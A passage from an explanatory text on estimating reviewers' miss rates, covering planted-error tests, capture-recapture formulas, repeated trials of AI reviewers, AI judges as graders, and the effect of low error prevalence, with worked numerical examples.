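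The example is realistic. When Litvak pooled every system's findings, they covered 93 of the 100 errors, and the other seven were all omissions. For one of the seven, Litvak had deleted a paper's statement that the researchers had reported all their measures and exclusions, and no system flagged its absence.

The rule of three offers even less assurance against deliberate changes, because it holds only if the errors in the test come from the same distribution as those in real work.

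### Estimating the errors nobody found

Planted errors show how well a reviewer catches known errors, while *capture-recapture* is used to estimate how many unknown errors remain in a real document. The method comes from biology. *Inferring the size of the causal universe* (2018) explains that biologists catch some animals, tag and release them, and later catch a second group. If many of the second group have tags, the population is probably small.

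Two reviewers can take the place of the two catches. Suppose that the first finds 12 errors in a contract, the second finds 10, and 8 are the same. The second reviewer found 8 of the first reviewer's 12, or two-thirds. If the second reviewer finds two-thirds of all errors, then 10 is two-thirds of the total, so the total is 15. The formula is

$$\text{estimated total} = \frac{n_1 \times n_2}{m} = \frac{12 \times 10}{8} = 15$$

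where n₁ and n₂ are the numbers that each reviewer found and m is the overlap. Together the reviewers know of 12 + 10 − 8 = 14 errors, so about one remains.

That estimate is sensitive to small changes in the overlap. If the overlap had been 7 instead of 8, the estimated total would be 17, with two errors still to find. If it had been 9, the estimated total would be 13.3, with almost no errors left to find.

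The formula's larger problem is its assumption that reviewers' findings are independent and that every error is equally easy to find. In the spreadsheet illustration, readers find each of four errors 96% of the time and each of another four 30% of the time. Two such readers would find about five errors each, with about four in common, so together they would know of about six. The formula would estimate a total of 6.3, and the search would seem almost finished, when on average two of the eight errors would remain.

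Errors that neither reviewer can see do not affect the estimate. If the contract also contained five omissions that both reviewers always overlook, they would still find 12 and 10 errors, with 8 in common, and the formula would still give 15 instead of the true total of 20. The method is especially doubtful for two AI reviewers because they tend to miss the same bugs.

*Effective Automated Decision Support for Managing Crowdtesting* (2018) lists some improved versions that allow for errors of different difficulty or reviewers of different ability. They need more data, and *Predicting Defect Content and Quality Assurance Effectiveness* (2014) puts the minimum for a usable estimate at four inspectors. None of these versions can count errors that nobody is able to find.

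With few errors the method breaks down altogether. If there is no overlap, the formula divides by zero. A common correction adds one to each number and subtracts one at the end, and *Context Engineering* (2026) applies it to a case in which one reviewer found nothing and the other found 12:

$$\frac{(0+1)(12+1)}{0+1} - 1 = 12$$

The corrected formula therefore estimates that the second reviewer found everything, although the only other reviewer found nothing that could confirm it.

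Capture-recapture is a reasonable way to decide whether a long document with many errors needs another reading, but it is of little use for a single decisive error. Estimating that one error remains doesn't reveal whether it is a misspelling or a missing "not". If the document contains only one error and both reviewers miss it, there are no detected errors to put into the formula.

### Repeated trials

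An AI reviewer can give different answers to the same question, so testing it only once on each question may be misleading. In *Humanity's First Exam*, Kelly, Kementsietsidis and colleagues (2026) measured this with 544 questions that people find easy, such as how many of the coffee mugs in a picture have no steam rising from them. They grouped the questions into sets of four close variants. The best five of 18 models answered 96% to 98% of the questions correctly on a single try. The same five averaged 86% on a stricter measure, which counted a set as passed only if the model got all four variants right on repeated attempts.

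All five models could solve every group when allowed several attempts, so they did not lack the ability. However, the questions were not a random sample, because each group started from a question that at least one model had already got wrong. Misread images caused 73% of the wrong answers, and the gap may be smaller for program code or contracts.

The 86% is higher than we would expect if errors were independent. In that case, a model that is right 97% of the time would have a 78% chance of getting all eight answers right across two attempts at each of four variants. The failures must therefore have been concentrated in certain groups. Whether misses are scattered or concentrated matters a great deal to someone who relies on a reviewer. These two imaginary reviewers each find 90% of errors in a single run.

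| Reviewer | Found in one run | Found in at least one of five runs | Found in all five runs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Has a 90% chance of finding any error | 90% | over 99.9% | 59% |
| Always finds nine errors in ten and never the tenth | 90% | 90% | 90% |

Running the first reviewer five times almost solves the problem. Running the second one again wastes money, and only a different kind of check would help. Litvak ran the general-purpose models three times each and reports that the repeats turned up no additional errors, so those models were more like the second reviewer.

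Repeated runs, like extra reviewers, also add false alarms. If each run has a 5% chance of wrongly flagging a correct change, the chance that at least one of five independent runs flags it is 23%.

Consistency matters more for decisive changes than for most work. A writing assistant that is right 97% of the time produces a good document with a few blemishes. But a reviewer usually sees each change only once, and if it overlooks a missing "not" on that run, the fact that it would catch the error on other runs doesn't help the people who sign the contract. A test should show the reviewer each planted error several times, in slightly different wording, and report both the average detection rate and how many errors the reviewer found every time.

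### AI judges as graders

Someone has to decide whether a comment such as "the sample sizes seem inconsistent" counts as finding a particular planted error. When there are hundreds of errors and a dozen reviewers, researchers usually use a language model to make this judgment.

The judge can be wrong in either direction. If a reviewer finds 99% of the errors but the judge fails to recognise 3% of the correct findings, the measured miss rate will be about 4%, mostly because of the judge's mistakes. A judge that too readily accepts findings as correct will hide misses, which is worse when the purpose is to show that the reviewer misses hardly any errors. Litvak had to revise the judging several times because the AI agent's first ways of matching comments to errors were too crude, and then checked only a few cases by hand.

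Zubeldia and colleagues were more careful. Models from three companies voted on each of 4,084 decisions and agreed unanimously on 93.5%. Another pass, with the full paper available, re-examined the doubtful cases and reversed 2.7% of all decisions. The judges were therefore consistent, but models from different companies can make the same mistake, and the researchers compared the judging with a human's on only one paper. They also entered their own reviewer, Skepthical, and used its mathematics module to decide which mathematical objections were false alarms. If the module misreads an equation during a review, it may well do so again when judging the objection.

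People should do more of the grading when the claim is strong, such as a miss rate below 1%. Suppose a judge credits the reviewer with catching 300 errors, and a person checks 60 of those credits and finds them all correct. By the rule of three, up to about 5% of the credits could still be wrong. That would be 15 hidden misses, far too many to support the claim. Checking all 300 by hand is tedious but takes much less time than making the test, because the person already knows where each error is.

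### When errors are far more common in the test than at work

Almost every test contains too many errors to resemble ordinary work. Litvak planted ten in each paper. Zubeldia and colleagues kept to four per copy so that the papers would look more natural. In the three collections that Risse and colleagues examined, the share of functions labelled vulnerable ranged from 4.5% to 47.9%, whereas in ordinary work it might be 0.1%.

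If the detection and false-alarm rates stay the same when errors are rarer, evaluators can recalculate precision for the lower prevalence. When the test uses the same instructions and kind of material as real use, the rates may stay the same for an AI reviewer that judges each item in a fresh session, because it can't learn from earlier items how common errors are. Human reviewers do learn how common errors are, so the low-prevalence effect will probably make their detection rate lower in real use than in the test.

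Testing at the true prevalence is rarely practical. If 0.1% of items contain errors, a test with 300 errors would require 300,000 items. An AI reviewer is easier to test by measuring its detection rate on planted errors and its false-alarm rate on a separate, large sample of ordinary sound work. The sample has to be large because the rule of three applies to false alarms too. In the example of 10,000 software changes, the false-alarm rate had to be 0.08% for half of the reviewer's flags to be right. To support that figure, the reviewer would have to clear about 3,750 sound changes with no false alarms.

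The best available way to measure how many errors human reviewers miss is to plant occasional errors in their real work, as airports do with images of weapons. This is slow. If ten programmers each review 50 changes a week and one change in 100 contains a planted error, the team will see five planted errors a week and need 60 weeks to see 300. The team also needs a reliable record of every planted error so that it can remove the ones reviewers miss.
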